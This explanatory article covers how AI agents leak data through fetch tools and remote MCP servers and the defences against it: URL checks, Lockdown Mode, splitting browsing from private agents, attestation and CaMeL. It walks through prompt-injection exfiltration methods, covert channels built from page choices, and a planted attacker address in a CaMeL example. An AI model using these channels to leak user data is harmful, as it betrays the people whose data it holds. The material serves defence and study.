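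Paul's website showed a special page to visitors that identified themselves as Claude. The page claimed that AI assistants had to log in by spelling out their user's name, following one link for each letter. Each link was already on a page that Claude had fetched, so the rule allowed it. Paul obtained the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic said it had already found the problem itself, and it stopped the chat app from following links inside fetched pages.

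Managed Agents still permits those links, according to the October release notes. Paul's method may therefore still work against an agent that runs there and has access to private data, unless the developer restricts which sites the agent can open.

The fourth row matters for third-party tools. Suppose the lawyer's converter is a confined local server, and the client application passes the converter's replies to Claude through the API. The converter can return the PDF with a link to a "conversion report" and encode a clause of the contract in the link's address. The rule lets the model open the link because the address came from a tool's reply. The API accepts addresses of up to 250 characters. If the host name takes 30 of them and each remaining character carries six bits, one fetch can send 165 bytes, or roughly two lines of text. Managed Agents would refuse this link.

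Addresses in the user's message can also come from strangers. Willison pointed out in 2025 that many applications paste outside text, such as an email, into the message the model receives as the user's.

Anthropic acknowledges a "residual risk" and advises developers to use the fetch tool only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive. It also suggests restricting domains, limiting the number of fetches or disabling the tool. Since 20 October, administrators have been able to turn fetching off for their whole organisation.

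Also on 7 October, Anthropic began applying the list of allowed hosts in a Managed Agents environment with limited networking to search and fetch as well as to code. If the list is empty, neither tool returns anything. Before the change, an agent in a restricted sandbox could still read the whole web through these tools.

### OpenAI's check: the address must already be public

OpenAI uses a different test, described in *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026). A separate crawler collects public addresses without access to users' conversations, and ChatGPT can automatically open addresses the crawler has already seen. For any other address, ChatGPT either looks for another source or warns the user that the link may include information from the conversation.

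OpenAI considered a list of trusted sites but found two problems. Many respectable sites have links that redirect to other sites, and a list strict enough to be safe would produce so many warnings that users would stop reading them.

This check would stop the converter's link, because the crawler could not have seen an address that the converter had just generated. According to OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection*, the same mechanism also applies to searches in Deep Research (ChatGPT's tool for long research tasks) and to navigation in Atlas (OpenAI's browser). If a request would send a third party something from the conversation, OpenAI blocks it or shows the user what would be sent.

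Some site owners ask OpenAI not to index their sites. ChatGPT then asks users to confirm every link to those sites, and users may approve these extra prompts without reading them.

Johann Rehberger reported the underlying problem to OpenAI in 2023. In Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, he calls the check a significant improvement but not a complete solution. He worries that not every team at OpenAI will use it, because the company's macOS and iOS apps once lacked an earlier version. An attacker can also publish pages, wait for the crawler to find them, and assign a meaning to each one.

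### Lockdown Mode

OpenAI offers a stricter setting, Lockdown Mode, for people with especially sensitive data. It limits ChatGPT's browsing to cached pages, copies that OpenAI already holds. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* says that no live requests leave the company's network during browsing. The page owner therefore sees nothing, whichever page the model chooses. OpenAI still sees the query, but it already has the conversation.

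According to OpenAI's *Lockdown Mode*, the setting disables deep research and agent mode, stops ChatGPT from downloading files for analysis, and prevents code written in Canvas, ChatGPT's editor, from using the network. Search results may be old or missing. Users can still upload files, so the lawyer could ask questions about the contract.

Lockdown Mode is available on free and paid personal plans, according to The Next Web's *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft*, although OpenAI says most people don't need it. Its protection has several gaps:

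- It doesn't affect network access in Codex.
- A user can turn it off for a single chat.
- In workspaces that a company manages, it does not automatically disable connected apps or MCP servers. Administrators have to choose which ones to allow.
- It doesn't stop prompt injection, so hidden text in an uploaded file can still make an answer wrong.

OpenAI does not guarantee that data can't leave. But refusing all live requests is a much simpler promise than recognising the dangerous ones.

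### How much a choice of page can reveal

A model that can't write its own addresses can still choose among existing ones, and the choice carries information. With *N* pages to choose from, one fetch conveys log₂ *N* bits, and *n* fetches convey *n* × log₂ *N*.

Suppose an attacker has 1,024 pages that the agent may open. Page 1 might stand for 0000000000, page 2 for 0000000001, and so on. Each fetch then conveys 10 bits, because 2¹⁰ is 1,024. A 128-bit encryption key, which is a common size, takes 13 fetches. The attacker then reconstructs the key from the log.

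This result depends on several assumptions:

1. The agent has access to the key and follows the attacker's instructions.
2. Every fetch reaches a server whose log the attacker can read, and the attacker can tell this agent's requests from other traffic.
3. The attacker sees the requests in order.
4. The agent can open the same page twice, and the second request is as visible as the first.
5. The model translates the key into page numbers without mistakes.

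The last assumption is the easiest to relax. The attacker could use just 16 pages, one for each hexadecimal digit, and the model would need only 32 fetches to spell out the key. Embrace The Red suggests 36 pages, one for each letter and digit, which a fairly large blog probably already has.

Caching weakens the second and fourth assumptions. If the provider keeps a copy of each page after the first visit, the attacker sees at most one request per page. If requests also arrive out of order, the attacker learns only which pages the agent opened. The table shows how many fetches it then takes to leak a 128-bit key.

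| Pages the attacker can use | Repeat visits visible, order known | Each page visible once, order known | Each page visible once, order unknown |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1,024 | 13 | 13 | 19 |
| 36 | 25 | 30 | Impossible, since 36 pages convey at most 36 bits |

Rehberger proposed caching or a ban on repeat visits to make this attack harder. Either would help a lot if the attack used a small set of pages, but very little if it used a large one. With 1,024 pages, a model that needs to visit only 13 can send about a tenth of a bit less in total if it never repeats one. Neither defense would have stopped Paul's nested links, since his site could produce a new address at every step.

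A cache built for speed is also an unreliable defence. Anthropic says its caching may change over time. Classmethod's *Claude's Web Fetch tool doesn't necessarily return the latest information* describes Claude repeatedly giving outdated limits from a page of Slack's documentation, and notes that the API has an option to bypass the cache. Lockdown Mode, by contrast, uses only stored copies, so a site can't see even the first visit.

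A fixed list of pages helps only if it leaves out the attacker's pages. If the lawyer's agent can open 1,024 pages on a court's website, the requests go to the court, so the attacker receives no bits. If the list includes a site where anyone can publish pages and read the visitor logs for them, the arithmetic above applies again. Lists also go out of date. Salesforce's agent product trusted a web domain whose registration had expired, and according to Willison, researchers registered it and received customer data there.

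Limiting the number of fetches limits how much data can leak. With 1,024 pages and five fetches, the attacker gets at most 50 bits. That leaves 78 bits of the key unknown, far too many to guess. But Anthropic's limit applies to each request to the model, and there is no default limit. An agent that could make five fetches in each of three requests could send 150 bits, enough to leak the whole key.

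Even 50 bits can spell a ten-letter company name at five bits a letter. Whether a deal is going ahead is only one bit, and an attacker with two pages can learn it from a single fetch by seeing which page the agent requests. Limiting the number of fetches can therefore protect a key or a long document, but not a short fact.

Without these restrictions, the model could write the whole key into one address using 22 characters. Anthropic's and OpenAI's rules therefore make large thefts slower and easier to notice. Thirteen visits to odd pages on one blog should look suspicious in a log, which helps only if someone checks the log in time.

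### Sorting tools by the channel they need

Users don't have to choose between giving every tool a connection and giving none of them one. Most tools fall into three groups.

| Channel the tool needs | Examples | What the tool loses without it |
|---|---|---|
| None | Document conversion, calculation | Little, such as pictures and fonts stored on the web |
| A narrow channel to a service that already holds the data | Calendar, company document store | Live data and the ability to make changes |
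| An open channel | Search, page fetching, messaging | Most of its purpose, unless stored copies or drafts will do |

The tools in the first group should start without network access. If one needs something from outside, the client application can often supply it in advance, as with the currency tool's list of exchange rates. The rates would be a day old, but that is good enough to give the lawyer a rough price in dollars.

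A calendar tool belongs in the second group. Reading appointments tells the service that stores them almost nothing new, but writing can leak data. If an agent puts a paragraph of the contract in an event and invites an outsider, the calendar service delivers that paragraph to them. In its advice for administrators using Lockdown Mode, OpenAI also treats reading from trusted apps as less risky than writing, and advises against writing wherever an attacker might see the result. A calendar tool without any connection could work from an exported copy, but it couldn't book a meeting.

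The third group varies more than the table suggests. A search tool can use a stored index instead of live requests, and a law firm could search its own copy of the statutes with no network access. A stored index would miss today's news, however. Without live requests, a fetch tool can return only saved pages. A messaging tool can still write drafts for the user to send, but that would not work for an assistant that answers messages overnight.

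### Keeping private data away from the agent that browses

An agent that needs the open web can still be safe if it holds nothing worth stealing. The user can split the work between a browsing agent, which has search and fetch but no private data, and a private agent, which has the contract but no way to contact anyone. For the lawyer's question about competition law, it might go like this:

1. The lawyer writes a general question: above what size does a company purchase need approval in this country?
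2. The browsing agent searches the web and returns notes. It has never seen the contract, and it has no memory of earlier chats.
3. The client application passes the notes to the private agent.
4. The private agent compares the thresholds in the notes with the figures in the contract and answers the lawyer.

A malicious page can still put a false threshold in the notes, or an instruction to send the contract somewhere. The private agent might use the false threshold, but it has no tool that could send the contract. The client application also must not load images or links in the private agent's answer, because the requests could carry data out.

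Memory is easy to overlook when splitting the work. Paul's attack stole details that the chat app had saved from past conversations, even though no confidential file was open. OpenAI says Lockdown Mode doesn't change memory. With memory turned on, if the lawyer discussed the contract in a locked chat and did research in an ordinary one, the second chat might have access to information from the first.

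The protection lasts only while data moves in one direction, from the browsing agent to the private agent. If the private agent could write the browsing agent's questions, an instruction planted in the notes could get the private agent to include a clause of the contract in a question. To reduce this risk, a person could check each question, or the private agent could choose from a fixed menu. With a menu of 16 questions, each choice could leak at most four bits.

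These precautions rule out any task in which the thing to look up is private. The agent can't check whether the company in the contract has been sued, because it would have to search for the company's name. It can't find flights that fit around a confidential meeting without revealing the dates, or research an error message that contains part of a firm's unpublished code. For some of these tasks, the browsing agent can download everything that might be relevant, and the private agent can search it offline. That works for a government's sanctions list, which is one file. For lawsuits it would mean copying a court's whole archive, and it isn't practical for flight prices, which change by the hour.

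## Remotely hosted tool servers

AgentBound and Wassette can limit a tool because they start it. A remote tool server is already running on a machine its operator controls when the client application connects to it. The user can refuse to connect or can send less data, but cannot take away the server's network access.

### Why the user cannot confine one

Suppose the lawyer connects the agent to a document converter at a web address instead of installing one. The client application sends the contract, and a PDF comes back. The four questions have poor answers:

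1. The operator starts the converter, so the lawyer's settings count for nothing.
2. The lawyer doesn't know what authority the converter has. It may keep a copy of the contract, pass it to a subcontractor, or use one running copy for all its customers.
3. Nobody on the lawyer's side can verify any of this. The encrypted connection proves that the client application reached the right web address, but proves nothing about the program there.
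4. The reply reaches the model, as it would from a local tool.

The operator can also change the code after the lawyer has approved the server. npm distributed the code for postmark-mcp, so anyone who looked could find the line its developer added. On a remote server, the same change would have left no trace on the user's machine.

Attackers can also take over a server run by an honest operator. Datadog, a monitoring company, has analysed a malware campaign named N4D that breaks into exposed MCP servers and other internet-facing services. The malware lists an MCP server's tools, runs one that executes commands, and reports the result to its controller. A user who approved the server before the break-in would still see the same address and tools.

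A further risk is that a server shared by many customers may expose one customer's data to another. In June 2025 Asana, which makes project-management software, found a bug in its MCP server that could have shown one organisation's data to another, according to AuthZed, a company that sells authorization software. The bug resembles Lampson's example of a program with memory. A factory would have given each customer a separate copy, but a customer of a remote service can't insist on that.

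If an operator shuts down a server and lets its domain registration lapse, a stranger could register the name and receive whatever client applications still send there. Researchers did this with an expired domain that Salesforce's agent trusted.

### Services that already hold the data, and intermediaries

The risk a remote server adds depends on what data its operator already has. If the lawyer's mail provider runs its own MCP server, connecting an agent to it gives the provider little new information, because the provider already stores every message. The provider does learn what the agent searches for and what it writes in drafts. An agent with the contract open could also include one of its clauses in a mailbox search.

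An intermediary runs a server that sits between the agent and someone else's service. To use such a server for email, the user has to give the intermediary a credential for the mailbox. The intermediary then sees the messages the agent requests, and it can also use the credential when no agent is running.

| Who runs the server | What they newly receive | What an attacker gains by breaking in |
|---|---|---|
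| The service that stores the data | The agent's searches and drafts | The access that connected customers have to that service |
| An intermediary | The data passing through, and a credential for the service | Access to every service that its users connected |
| A stranger's converter | Each document that users send | Every document the operator kept, and new ones as they arrive |

Some services host their own tool servers, and GitGuardian, a security company, gives the error-tracking service Sentry as an example. It contrasts Sentry with Smithery.ai, a registry that hosts servers written by other people, which users would otherwise have run themselves. Hosting by a registry saves users from installing anything, but they must trust one more company.

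GitGuardian found a serious flaw in that arrangement. Smithery built each server from its developer's GitHub repository without properly checking the configured path to the build folder. An attacker could change the path and read sensitive files from the build machine. According to Plushcap, which summarises technical blogs, an attacker could then have run code on the hosted servers and possibly intercepted users' data. Smithery fixed the flaw quickly after GitGuardian reported it. Until then, users of any one server had to trust every other developer who could submit a build.

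In April 2026, attackers reached the web host Vercel through Context.ai, an outside AI tool that at least one Vercel employee used. The tool had access to the employee's Google account, and the attackers compromised that access and moved from the account into Vercel's internal systems, where they read unencrypted settings, according to Adrian, in *Hacker fordert von Vercel 2 Millionen USD Lösegeld*. Someone then demanded $2 million and offered for sale what they claimed were Vercel's access keys and source code. Context.ai may not have used MCP, but a tool server run by an intermediary holds the same sort of credential.

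Attackers seem to have noticed how much these intermediaries hold. Microsoft (2026) described an intrusion into RAGFlow, software for building AI applications on a company's documents, in which the attacker added code to the part that saves credentials for language-model providers. That code could intercept each new credential as someone entered it, so replacing a stolen key would not help until the code was removed.

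### The Mittwald breach

Mittwald, a German web-hosting company, offered its customers an MCP server that connected AI assistants to mStudio, its control panel for websites and hosting. Mittwald already stored the customers' websites, so this was the type of server that gives its operator little new data. In October 2026 an attacker exploited a flaw in the server to get into 56 customer projects.

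Robert Meyer, Mittwald's managing director, published a timeline on 7 November. David (2026), in *MCP Security Best Practices After the Mittwald Breach*, gives the details in English:

| Date | What happened |
|---|---|
| 21 October | The attacker first tested the flaw, on an evening when many administrators were busy with an unrelated PHP vulnerability |
| From 23 October | The attacker registered test accounts and behaved much like a normal customer, apart from some simple injection attacks |
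| 27 October | The attacker registered another account and exploited the flaw five minutes later |
| 4 November | Mittwald noticed unusual behaviour, identified the MCP server as the entry point and switched it off |
| 5 November | Mittwald blocked the projects with traces of the attacker, and disabled mStudio logins and remote access over SSH |
| 6 November | Mittwald finished examining 56 compromised projects and found no others |
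| 7 November | mStudio and SSH came back |

The flaw exposed session tokens, which a service issues after a login so that the user doesn't have to log in again. The service accepts a token from anyone who presents it, so the attacker didn't need passwords. Two-factor authentication would not have helped, because it protects the login and the tokens came from customers who had already logged in.

Each token gave access to mStudio with its owner's rights, including every project the owner could reach. Agencies often manage sites for many clients, so a single stolen token may have given access to dozens of projects. The figure of 56 is the number of projects, so it can't be used to tell how many customers lost a token.

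Mittwald revoked all tokens and blocked customers' API keys as a precaution. But an attacker who had been inside a project could have left another way in. According to KIberblick's *Mittwald* (2026), Mittwald advises anyone who used the server after 27 October to assume that the attacker got in, delete any keys and SSH users they don't recognise, and replace the credentials for databases, mail accounts and outside services stored in their projects. Mittwald found no sign that anyone had published customer data. It is telling affected customers individually whether the attacker retrieved files, databases or mailboxes.

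On the night before 12 November, attackers struck again through a flaw in Mittwald's website. Mittwald took the site offline and again shut off mStudio and SSH, then restored them on 13 November. It found no sign that the attackers had accessed internal systems. The MCP server stayed offline, and Mittwald directed customers to its command-line tool instead.

Meyer believes the attacker used AI tools, because only seconds passed between some steps that would have taken a person much longer. That is thin evidence, since an ordinary script is just as fast. Martin (2026) notes in *Alleged AI-aided cyberattack exploits assistant interface to breach German web host* that Mittwald offered no other evidence.

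More importantly, Mittwald has not disclosed whether the flaw was in its own code or in an open-source MCP library. The company promised a detailed report for the week of 9 November but had not published it by the 13th. If the flaw was in a library, other operators that use it may have the same flaw, and their customers have no way to check.

### What a directory review can establish

Some registries and makers of client applications review servers before listing them. A reviewer can confirm who runs a server, read the tool descriptions for hidden instructions, and call each tool to see whether it works. But the reviewer sees a remote server only from the outside, as a user does, so a document converter that returned a good PDF and kept a copy of every contract would pass.

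A review also goes out of date. Many of the servers Kraishan tracked had changed what they advertise, and some had moved to a different host. A dishonest operator could behave well only for the reviewer, much as Paul's website showed a special page to Claude.

Reading the source code is a better check, when the operator publishes it. Akamai, which sells web security and delivery services, used an AI-assisted tool to examine about 300 official MCP servers, meaning those from the makers of the products they connect to. It found vulnerabilities in the servers for three widely used products: the databases Apache Pinot and Apache Doris, and Alibaba's database service. That is a low rate, but the review covered only how the servers communicate with the systems behind them. Users can tell from an "official" label who published a server, which would have exposed the copy of Postmark's server, but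 not whether the code is sound. Users of a remote server also can't tell whether the operator is running the published code.

### Credentials that open less

A user who can't limit the server can still limit what its credential gives access to. The service that issues the credential enforces the limit, so it applies even if the server is dishonest or an attacker has taken it over.

Suppose an agency has 40 client websites with one hosting company and wants an agent to update one of them. Someone who steals a token with the agency's full rights can reach all 40 sites, while a token limited to one project exposes only that site. Making the limited token read-only would also stop the thief from adding an SSH user, but the thief could still copy the site, and the agent couldn't use the token to make the update. KIberblick advises users of similar connectors to check whether they can restrict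 a token in these ways. Users often have no choice, because the service has to offer narrower tokens and the server has to work with them.

Short token lifetimes give only limited protection. If tokens expire after an hour, a thief who copies the server's stored tokens can use only those issued in the past hour. But the attacker had access to Mittwald's server for eight days, and each customer who connected during that time would have supplied a fresh token. Many services also issue a longer-lasting refresh token, which can be used to get new short-lived tokens. If the remote server holds both, the short lifetime protects very little. The client application should keep the refresh token and give the server only the short-lived one.

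Since June 2025, MCP's authorization rules have required a server to accept only tokens issued for that server and have forbidden it to pass those tokens on to other services. This prevents a malicious server from collecting a token and using it elsewhere. The rules don't limit what a token gives access to on the server it was issued for, which was the problem at Mittwald.

#### Servers that use one person's rights for another

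A server can also misuse a credential by accident. *Give Them an Inch and They Will Take a Mile* (Huang, Dai et al., 2026) describes servers that ask for authorization once, save it, and reuse it for every later call without checking who is calling. A stranger who can reach such a server over the network can make calls with the first user's rights without stealing the credential.

The researchers built a tool that follows each possible path from a tool call to a sensitive operation and checks whether the code authorizes the caller along the way. They ran it on 6,137 servers and found that 2,846 (46.4%) had missing, cached or reused authorization. Among servers for software developers, the share was 52%. They also examined 87 open-source MCP projects with over 1,000 stars each and found eight with flaws that could let an attacker run commands on the server.

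The 46.4% figure probably overstates the danger for people who run a server on their own laptop, where most callers are their own programs. The same habit is much more serious on a remote server with many customers.

In 1988, Norman Hardy of KeyKOS described this kind of mistake, in which a program uses its own rights on behalf of someone who doesn't have them, and called it the confused deputy. In a capability system, the caller hands over the capability along with the request, so the program doesn't have to guess whose rights to use. A remote MCP server could work similarly if each call carried the caller's own narrowly scoped token and the server stored none.

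### Sending less data

The most reliable way to keep data from a remote server is not to send it. Suppose the lawyer's currency tool is now a remote service. If the agent asks it to convert the contract price, the operator learns the price. The agent can instead ask for the value of one euro and leave the multiplication to the client application, so that the operator learns only that someone wanted the rate.

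Text is harder. If the lawyer needs a clause translated, the client application could replace the companies' names with "Party A" and "Party B" and the price with a placeholder, then restore the originals in the reply. The translator would learn that someone is buying a company, and perhaps the industry, but not which company. A clause about an unusual product could still identify the company.

The client application should make the substitutions, because a model influenced by a malicious tool description might leave the names in. The client also has to apply them to follow-up requests, since a remote server can use an `input_required` result to prompt the user for the details that the first call left out.

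Sending less works for tools that need only part of the agent's data. But a remote converter needs the whole contract, and an email intermediary needs the mailbox. Sending less also would not have helped Mittwald's customers, because the attacker took tokens that the server needed to work.

### Running a copy locally

If the developer publishes the server's code, the user can run it locally and confine it as AgentBound does. Many remote servers are only a thin layer over an online service, and a local copy still has to contact that service, but it does so without an intermediary. The credential stays on the user's machine, and an address allowlist can limit the copy to that service. Mittwald's command-line tool is similar in that customers run it themselves.

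The user then has to know which code is running, which is harder than choosing a version number. Help Net Security's *Your pinned MCP server may not be as pinned as you think* (2026) describes what James Lagermann found in the lab of Corelight, a network security company. An administrator's workstation started its MCP servers with uvx, a program that downloads a Python package and runs it. The settings named one exact release of one server and stayed the same for five weeks, but in that time the server ran with 15 different sets of dependencies, the third-party packages it relies on. Of its 69 packages, 23 changed version, including the cryptography library and the MCP software development kit.

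The launcher had pinned the server but not its dependencies. It ignored the project's lock file, which lists the exact dependencies with their cryptographic hashes, and fetched new ones each time it rebuilt the server's environment. A hijacked package may be available for only minutes or hours before someone removes it, so frequent rebuilding makes a user more likely to install one. The servers on this workstation had credentials for 11 management systems, including the company's firewall and security monitoring. Corelight then examined 35 MCP servers from its lab and two vendors' catalogues and found the same weakness in the recommended installation methods for 23 of them.

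Corelight's remedy was to freeze a server at an exact commit (a saved state of the code), install it once from a lock file with hashes, start the program directly and turn off update checks. Over two weeks, five frozen servers started 457 times with no change in their packages. Frozen code doesn't receive security fixes, though. When the team froze one server, 40 of its packages were already older than those the launcher would have fetched that day. Lagermann reviews the servers he maintains for vulnerabilities every night, but most users of a converter won't do as much.

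Limiting a tool's network access reduces the need for this work. An old bug in an encryption library hardly matters in a frozen converter with no network connection, but it matters a great deal in a server that holds a firewall's password.

### Attested Tool-Server Admission

Some remote servers have no published code to copy. For these, one proposal has the client application check a signed document before it connects. Metere (2026), in *Attested Tool-Server Admission*, describes a system that his company, Enclawed, includes in its software for running agents. It works like this:

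1. The server's operator writes a short document that names the server, its publisher, its version and the most sensitive class of data it may handle. The holder of a key that the client application already trusts signs the document.
2. The operator puts the document at a standard address on the server's own site.
3. Before the first call, the client application fetches the document. It checks the signature, whether the signer may vouch for that class of data, and whether the class is high enough for the data in question.
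4. If the document lists the hosts it applies to, the client application checks that it has connected to one of them.
5. For every call, the client application also checks the tool's name against a short list that the user's organisation approved for this server, and refuses any other tool.
6. It records each decision in a log in which later changes would show.

If the document fails a check, the strict version of the software blocks the connection, while the open version warns the user and lets them go ahead.

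The document is a statement by the signer and contains no fingerprint of the running program, so an operator could replace all of the server's code and the signature would still verify. Metere acknowledges that the system doesn't stop an admitted server from misbehaving within its approved tools and doesn't inspect the data that crosses the connection. Signers also can't yet revoke a document early. A signed document from Mittwald would have passed every check throughout the eight days the attacker had access.

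The test results are weaker evidence than the large counts suggest. Metere had a language model write attacks on the checks and ran them against simulated servers. The software refused all 31 disguised tool names and all 12 invalid documents, and it accepted the valid ones. A small model, Llama 3.2, then generated 27,025 distinct tool names and 14,378 distinct forged documents, and the software refused them all. But the software accepts a tool name only if it matches the list exactly, so the 27,025 wrong names mostly test the same comparison. A forger without the signing key can't produce a valid signature, however many attempts it makes. These tests can find programming mistakes, and the written attacks found that an earlier version accepted a valid document from the wrong host, which is why step 4 exists. The tests don't show whether an admitted server keeps a copy of what it receives.

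The list of approved tools is the part most likely to help users today. Enclawed built the system to connect its agent to Google's own Gmail server, and its list for that server includes searching mail and creating drafts but not deleting messages. In a live test, the software allowed a listed tool and refused an unlisted one before any network call. A similar list for GitHub's server that left out the tool for opening pull requests would have stopped the GitHub attack at its last step. Google doesn't publish a signed document of this kind, so for Gmail, Enclawed skips steps 1 to 4 and relies on its own signed connector.

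Metere wants MCP to adopt the format, because a signed document is useful only to client applications that recognise it. The format was not yet part of the standard. The paper lists submitting it to MCP's maintainers as future work, although its acknowledgements cite a numbered proposal in the project's repository.

### Could attested hardware prove that a server is confined?

Despite its name, Attested Tool-Server Admission doesn't use the hardware feature called remote attestation. Some processors from Intel and AMD can run a program in encrypted memory that the machine's owner can't normally read, and can produce a signed report of which program they loaded. A remote converter could use this to give the lawyer evidence about its code:

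1. The operator publishes the converter's complete software, in a form from which anyone can calculate its hash.
2. The operator starts the software in protected memory, and the processor calculates the same hash.
3. The client application connects and sends a random number, so that the operator can't replay an old report.
4. The processor signs a report containing the hash, the random number and an encryption key that exists only inside the protected memory.
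5. The client application checks that the signature traces back to the processor's manufacturer and that the hash is the one it expects. It then encrypts the contract with that key and sends it.

The operator could no longer replace the code without the client application detecting the change, which addresses the complaint that users can't tell what a remote server runs.

However, the report identifies the software but doesn't cover its network connections, so the lawyer has to work out from the software whether the converter can send the contract elsewhere. For a large program, that is no easier than reading the source of a local one. The practical solution is to put a small, trusted layer in the protected memory with the tool. That layer could be a WebAssembly runtime that gives the converter no network function and encrypts the reply so that only the caller can read it. Experts would need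 to examine the layer once. The converter's code could stay secret, as in a KeyKOS factory, because the layer would confine it whatever it did.

Such a service would be the closest equivalent to a factory on someone else's machine. It would suit converters and calculators, but not a tool that depends on an ordinary online service, because data sent to that online service would leave the protected memory. Updates would also be a burden. If an operator rebuilt its software as often as the launcher on Corelight's workstation did, client applications would see 15 different hashes for the same version number in five weeks, and someone would have to approve each one. A report that identifies the expected code also doesn't protect against flaws in that code, like the one that exposed Mittwald's tokens.

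The work on MCP servers is at an early stage. An open-source project called attestable-mcp-server runs an MCP server in Intel's protected memory and puts the processor's report in the server's certificate, so a client application can check the code before connecting. The project is a demonstration, and it doesn't address whether that code has other connections. MCP has no standard message for such reports, so the client application and the server have to agree on their own method.

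Apple has taken the idea further, outside MCP, with Private Cloud Compute, which it announced in 2024 to handle AI requests that are too large for a phone. Apple's devices send data only to servers that can prove they are running software listed in a public log, and outside researchers can inspect that software. But Apple designed the hardware, the servers and the devices that check them. For a stranger's converter to work this way, client applications from many companies would have to accept reports about software from many developers.

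The operator the lawyer is worried about may also be able to attack the hardware. In October 2025, researchers at Georgia Tech and Purdue University published an attack called TEE.fail. Using equipment costing less than $1,000, they recorded the traffic between a server's processor and its memory and extracted keys that sign attestation reports. Someone with such a key can forge a convincing report for an unprotected machine. The attack requires physical access to the server, which an operator with its own machines has. An operator that rents machines from a large cloud provider probably can't touch them, but the lawyer then has to trust the provider and needs some proof that the machine is in the provider's data centre.

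## CaMeL: tracking where data may go between tools

Confining each tool does not stop the language model from passing data from one tool to another, as it did in the GitHub attack. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*, a 2025 Google DeepMind paper by Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues, describes a system that controls this flow, called CaMeL ("capabilities for machine learning"). CaMeL keeps outside text away from the model that decides what to do, and it attaches to each piece of data a record of where the data came from and who may read it. These protections don't depend on a model recognising malicious text.

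### Two models and an interpreter

CaMeL builds on *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023), which suggested splitting an agent's work between two models. A planning model takes the user's request and can call tools, but never receives untrusted content. A reading model handles that content and has no tools. When the reading model summarises an email, the planning model gets only a reference to the summary, which it can pass to a tool.

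Debenedetti and colleagues found a gap in this design, and Willison (2025) acknowledged it in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*. Suppose a user asks the agent to send Bob a document, and Bob's address is in some meeting notes. The planning model writes the right steps, but the reading model has to find the address, and an attacker who can edit the notes can plant a different one. The agent then follows the plan exactly but sends the document to the attacker.

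CaMeL closes the gap with an interpreter, a program that runs other programs line by line. The planning model writes its plan as a short program in a restricted version of Python, with each tool available as a function. The interpreter gives every value a label that lists its sources and permitted readers. A value computed from others inherits their labels. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks the labels on the arguments against a policy for that tool. The check is ordinary code, so the wording of an email can't change its result.

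The CaMeL paper calls these labels capabilities. Each one stays with a piece of data and limits where that data can go, unlike a KeyKOS capability, which lets a program use a resource.

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, by Costa, Köpf and colleagues at Microsoft (2025), gives the usual rule for combining labels. The result keeps the sources of all its inputs, and only people who may read every input may read the result. If the lawyer, Bob and Carol may read one file, and the lawyer, Bob and Dan may read another, then only the lawyer and Bob may read a text based on both.

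### Sending Bob a document

Suppose the lawyer asks the agent to send Bob the document he requested in their last meeting, and says that the notes contain his address and the document's title. Bob and Carol were at the meeting, and both can edit the notes. The planning model sees this request and the tool descriptions, and writes:

```python
notes = get_meeting_notes()
address = ask_reader("Find Bob's email address", notes)
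title = ask_reader("Which document did Bob ask for?", notes)
document = fetch_document(title)
send_email(to=address, attachment=document)
```

The policy in this example lets the agent email a document only to people who may read it.

| Value | Sources | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|
| `notes` | The notes file | Lawyer, Bob, Carol |
| `address` | The notes file, through the reading model | Lawyer, Bob, Carol |
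| `title` | The notes file, through the reading model | Lawyer, Bob, Carol |
| `document` | The document store, and the notes file through `title` | Lawyer, Bob |

The document store lets the lawyer, Bob and Dan read the document. The last row omits Dan because the notes determined the title, and he may not read the notes.

If the notes contain Bob's real address, the interpreter finds him among the document's readers and sends the email. Now suppose that someone has broken into Carol's account and replaced the address with `bob@attacker.example`:

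1. The interpreter fetches the notes and labels them.
2. The reading model returns the planted address, which is a correct answer to the question it received.
3. The interpreter fetches the document and works out its permitted readers.
4. At `send_email`, it finds that nobody with the planted address may read the document. It refuses the call, or shows the lawyer the address and its source and asks for a decision.

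Willison describes a stricter policy that allows only recipients the user already trusts. Under that policy, the system would ask the user about any unfamiliar address from the notes, even a correct one. Using the readers' list avoids the extra question, but it only works if the document store has Bob's address and the attacker cannot change who has access.

An attacker who changes the title in the notes could still make Bob receive the wrong document, if he is allowed to read it. But planted text that tells the agent to forward other files has no effect, because the reading model has no tools and the program has no line that forwards them. The GitHub attack would fail for the same reason. A program for looking at open issues would fetch them, have the reading model summarise them, and show the lawyer the summary, but it would have no line that opens a private repository.

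The split can also reduce how many companies see data such as the contract. Willison notes that the planning model's provider never receives what the tools return, and that the reading model can be small enough to run on the user's own machine.

### Security and lost tasks on AgentDojo

Researchers usually test these systems on AgentDojo, a benchmark that simulates an office suite, a Slack workspace, a bank and a travel service. It pairs 97 ordinary tasks with planted instructions to make several hundred attack runs. The CaMeL paper says the system "effectively solves" the benchmark. Other teams have since repeated the test with newer models or different set-ups.

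*SecureClaw* (2026) adapted CaMeL's released code to run on the whole benchmark. None of the 629 attacks succeeded against CaMeL, but it completed only 29 of the 97 ordinary tasks, compared with 59 for SecureClaw's own system. The figure of 29 may understate what CaMeL can do, because a team has less reason to tune a rival system carefully.

In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) tested CaMeL in systems where one agent gives work to others. The team includes one of CaMeL's original developers. On a version of AgentDojo rebuilt for such systems, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL and 0.2% when every agent used it, averaged over five models. The team set no policies, so the separation of planning from reading produced nearly all of this improvement.

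The average combines very different results across models. Without CaMeL, attacks succeeded 36.1% of the time on GPT-4.1, an older model, but never on GPT-5.5. The benchmark's attacks are now too weak to show how much protection CaMeL adds to the best models, although stronger attacks still work on all of them. CaMeL's advantage is that its protection does not depend on the model resisting the attack.

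The same team tested CaMeL on AssetOpsBench, a set of industrial maintenance tasks. It lowered the share of tasks completed by 21.6 percentage points on average, but by 13.4 points for the two strongest models, which seem to be better at writing a whole plan in advance. The researchers also had to add each tool's reply format to its description, because the planning model writes code to process replies that it never sees. Someone has to do this once for each tool on every server a user connects.

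*The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reports that turning on policy checks halves the number of AgentDojo banking tasks that CaMeL completes.

### FIDES and later systems

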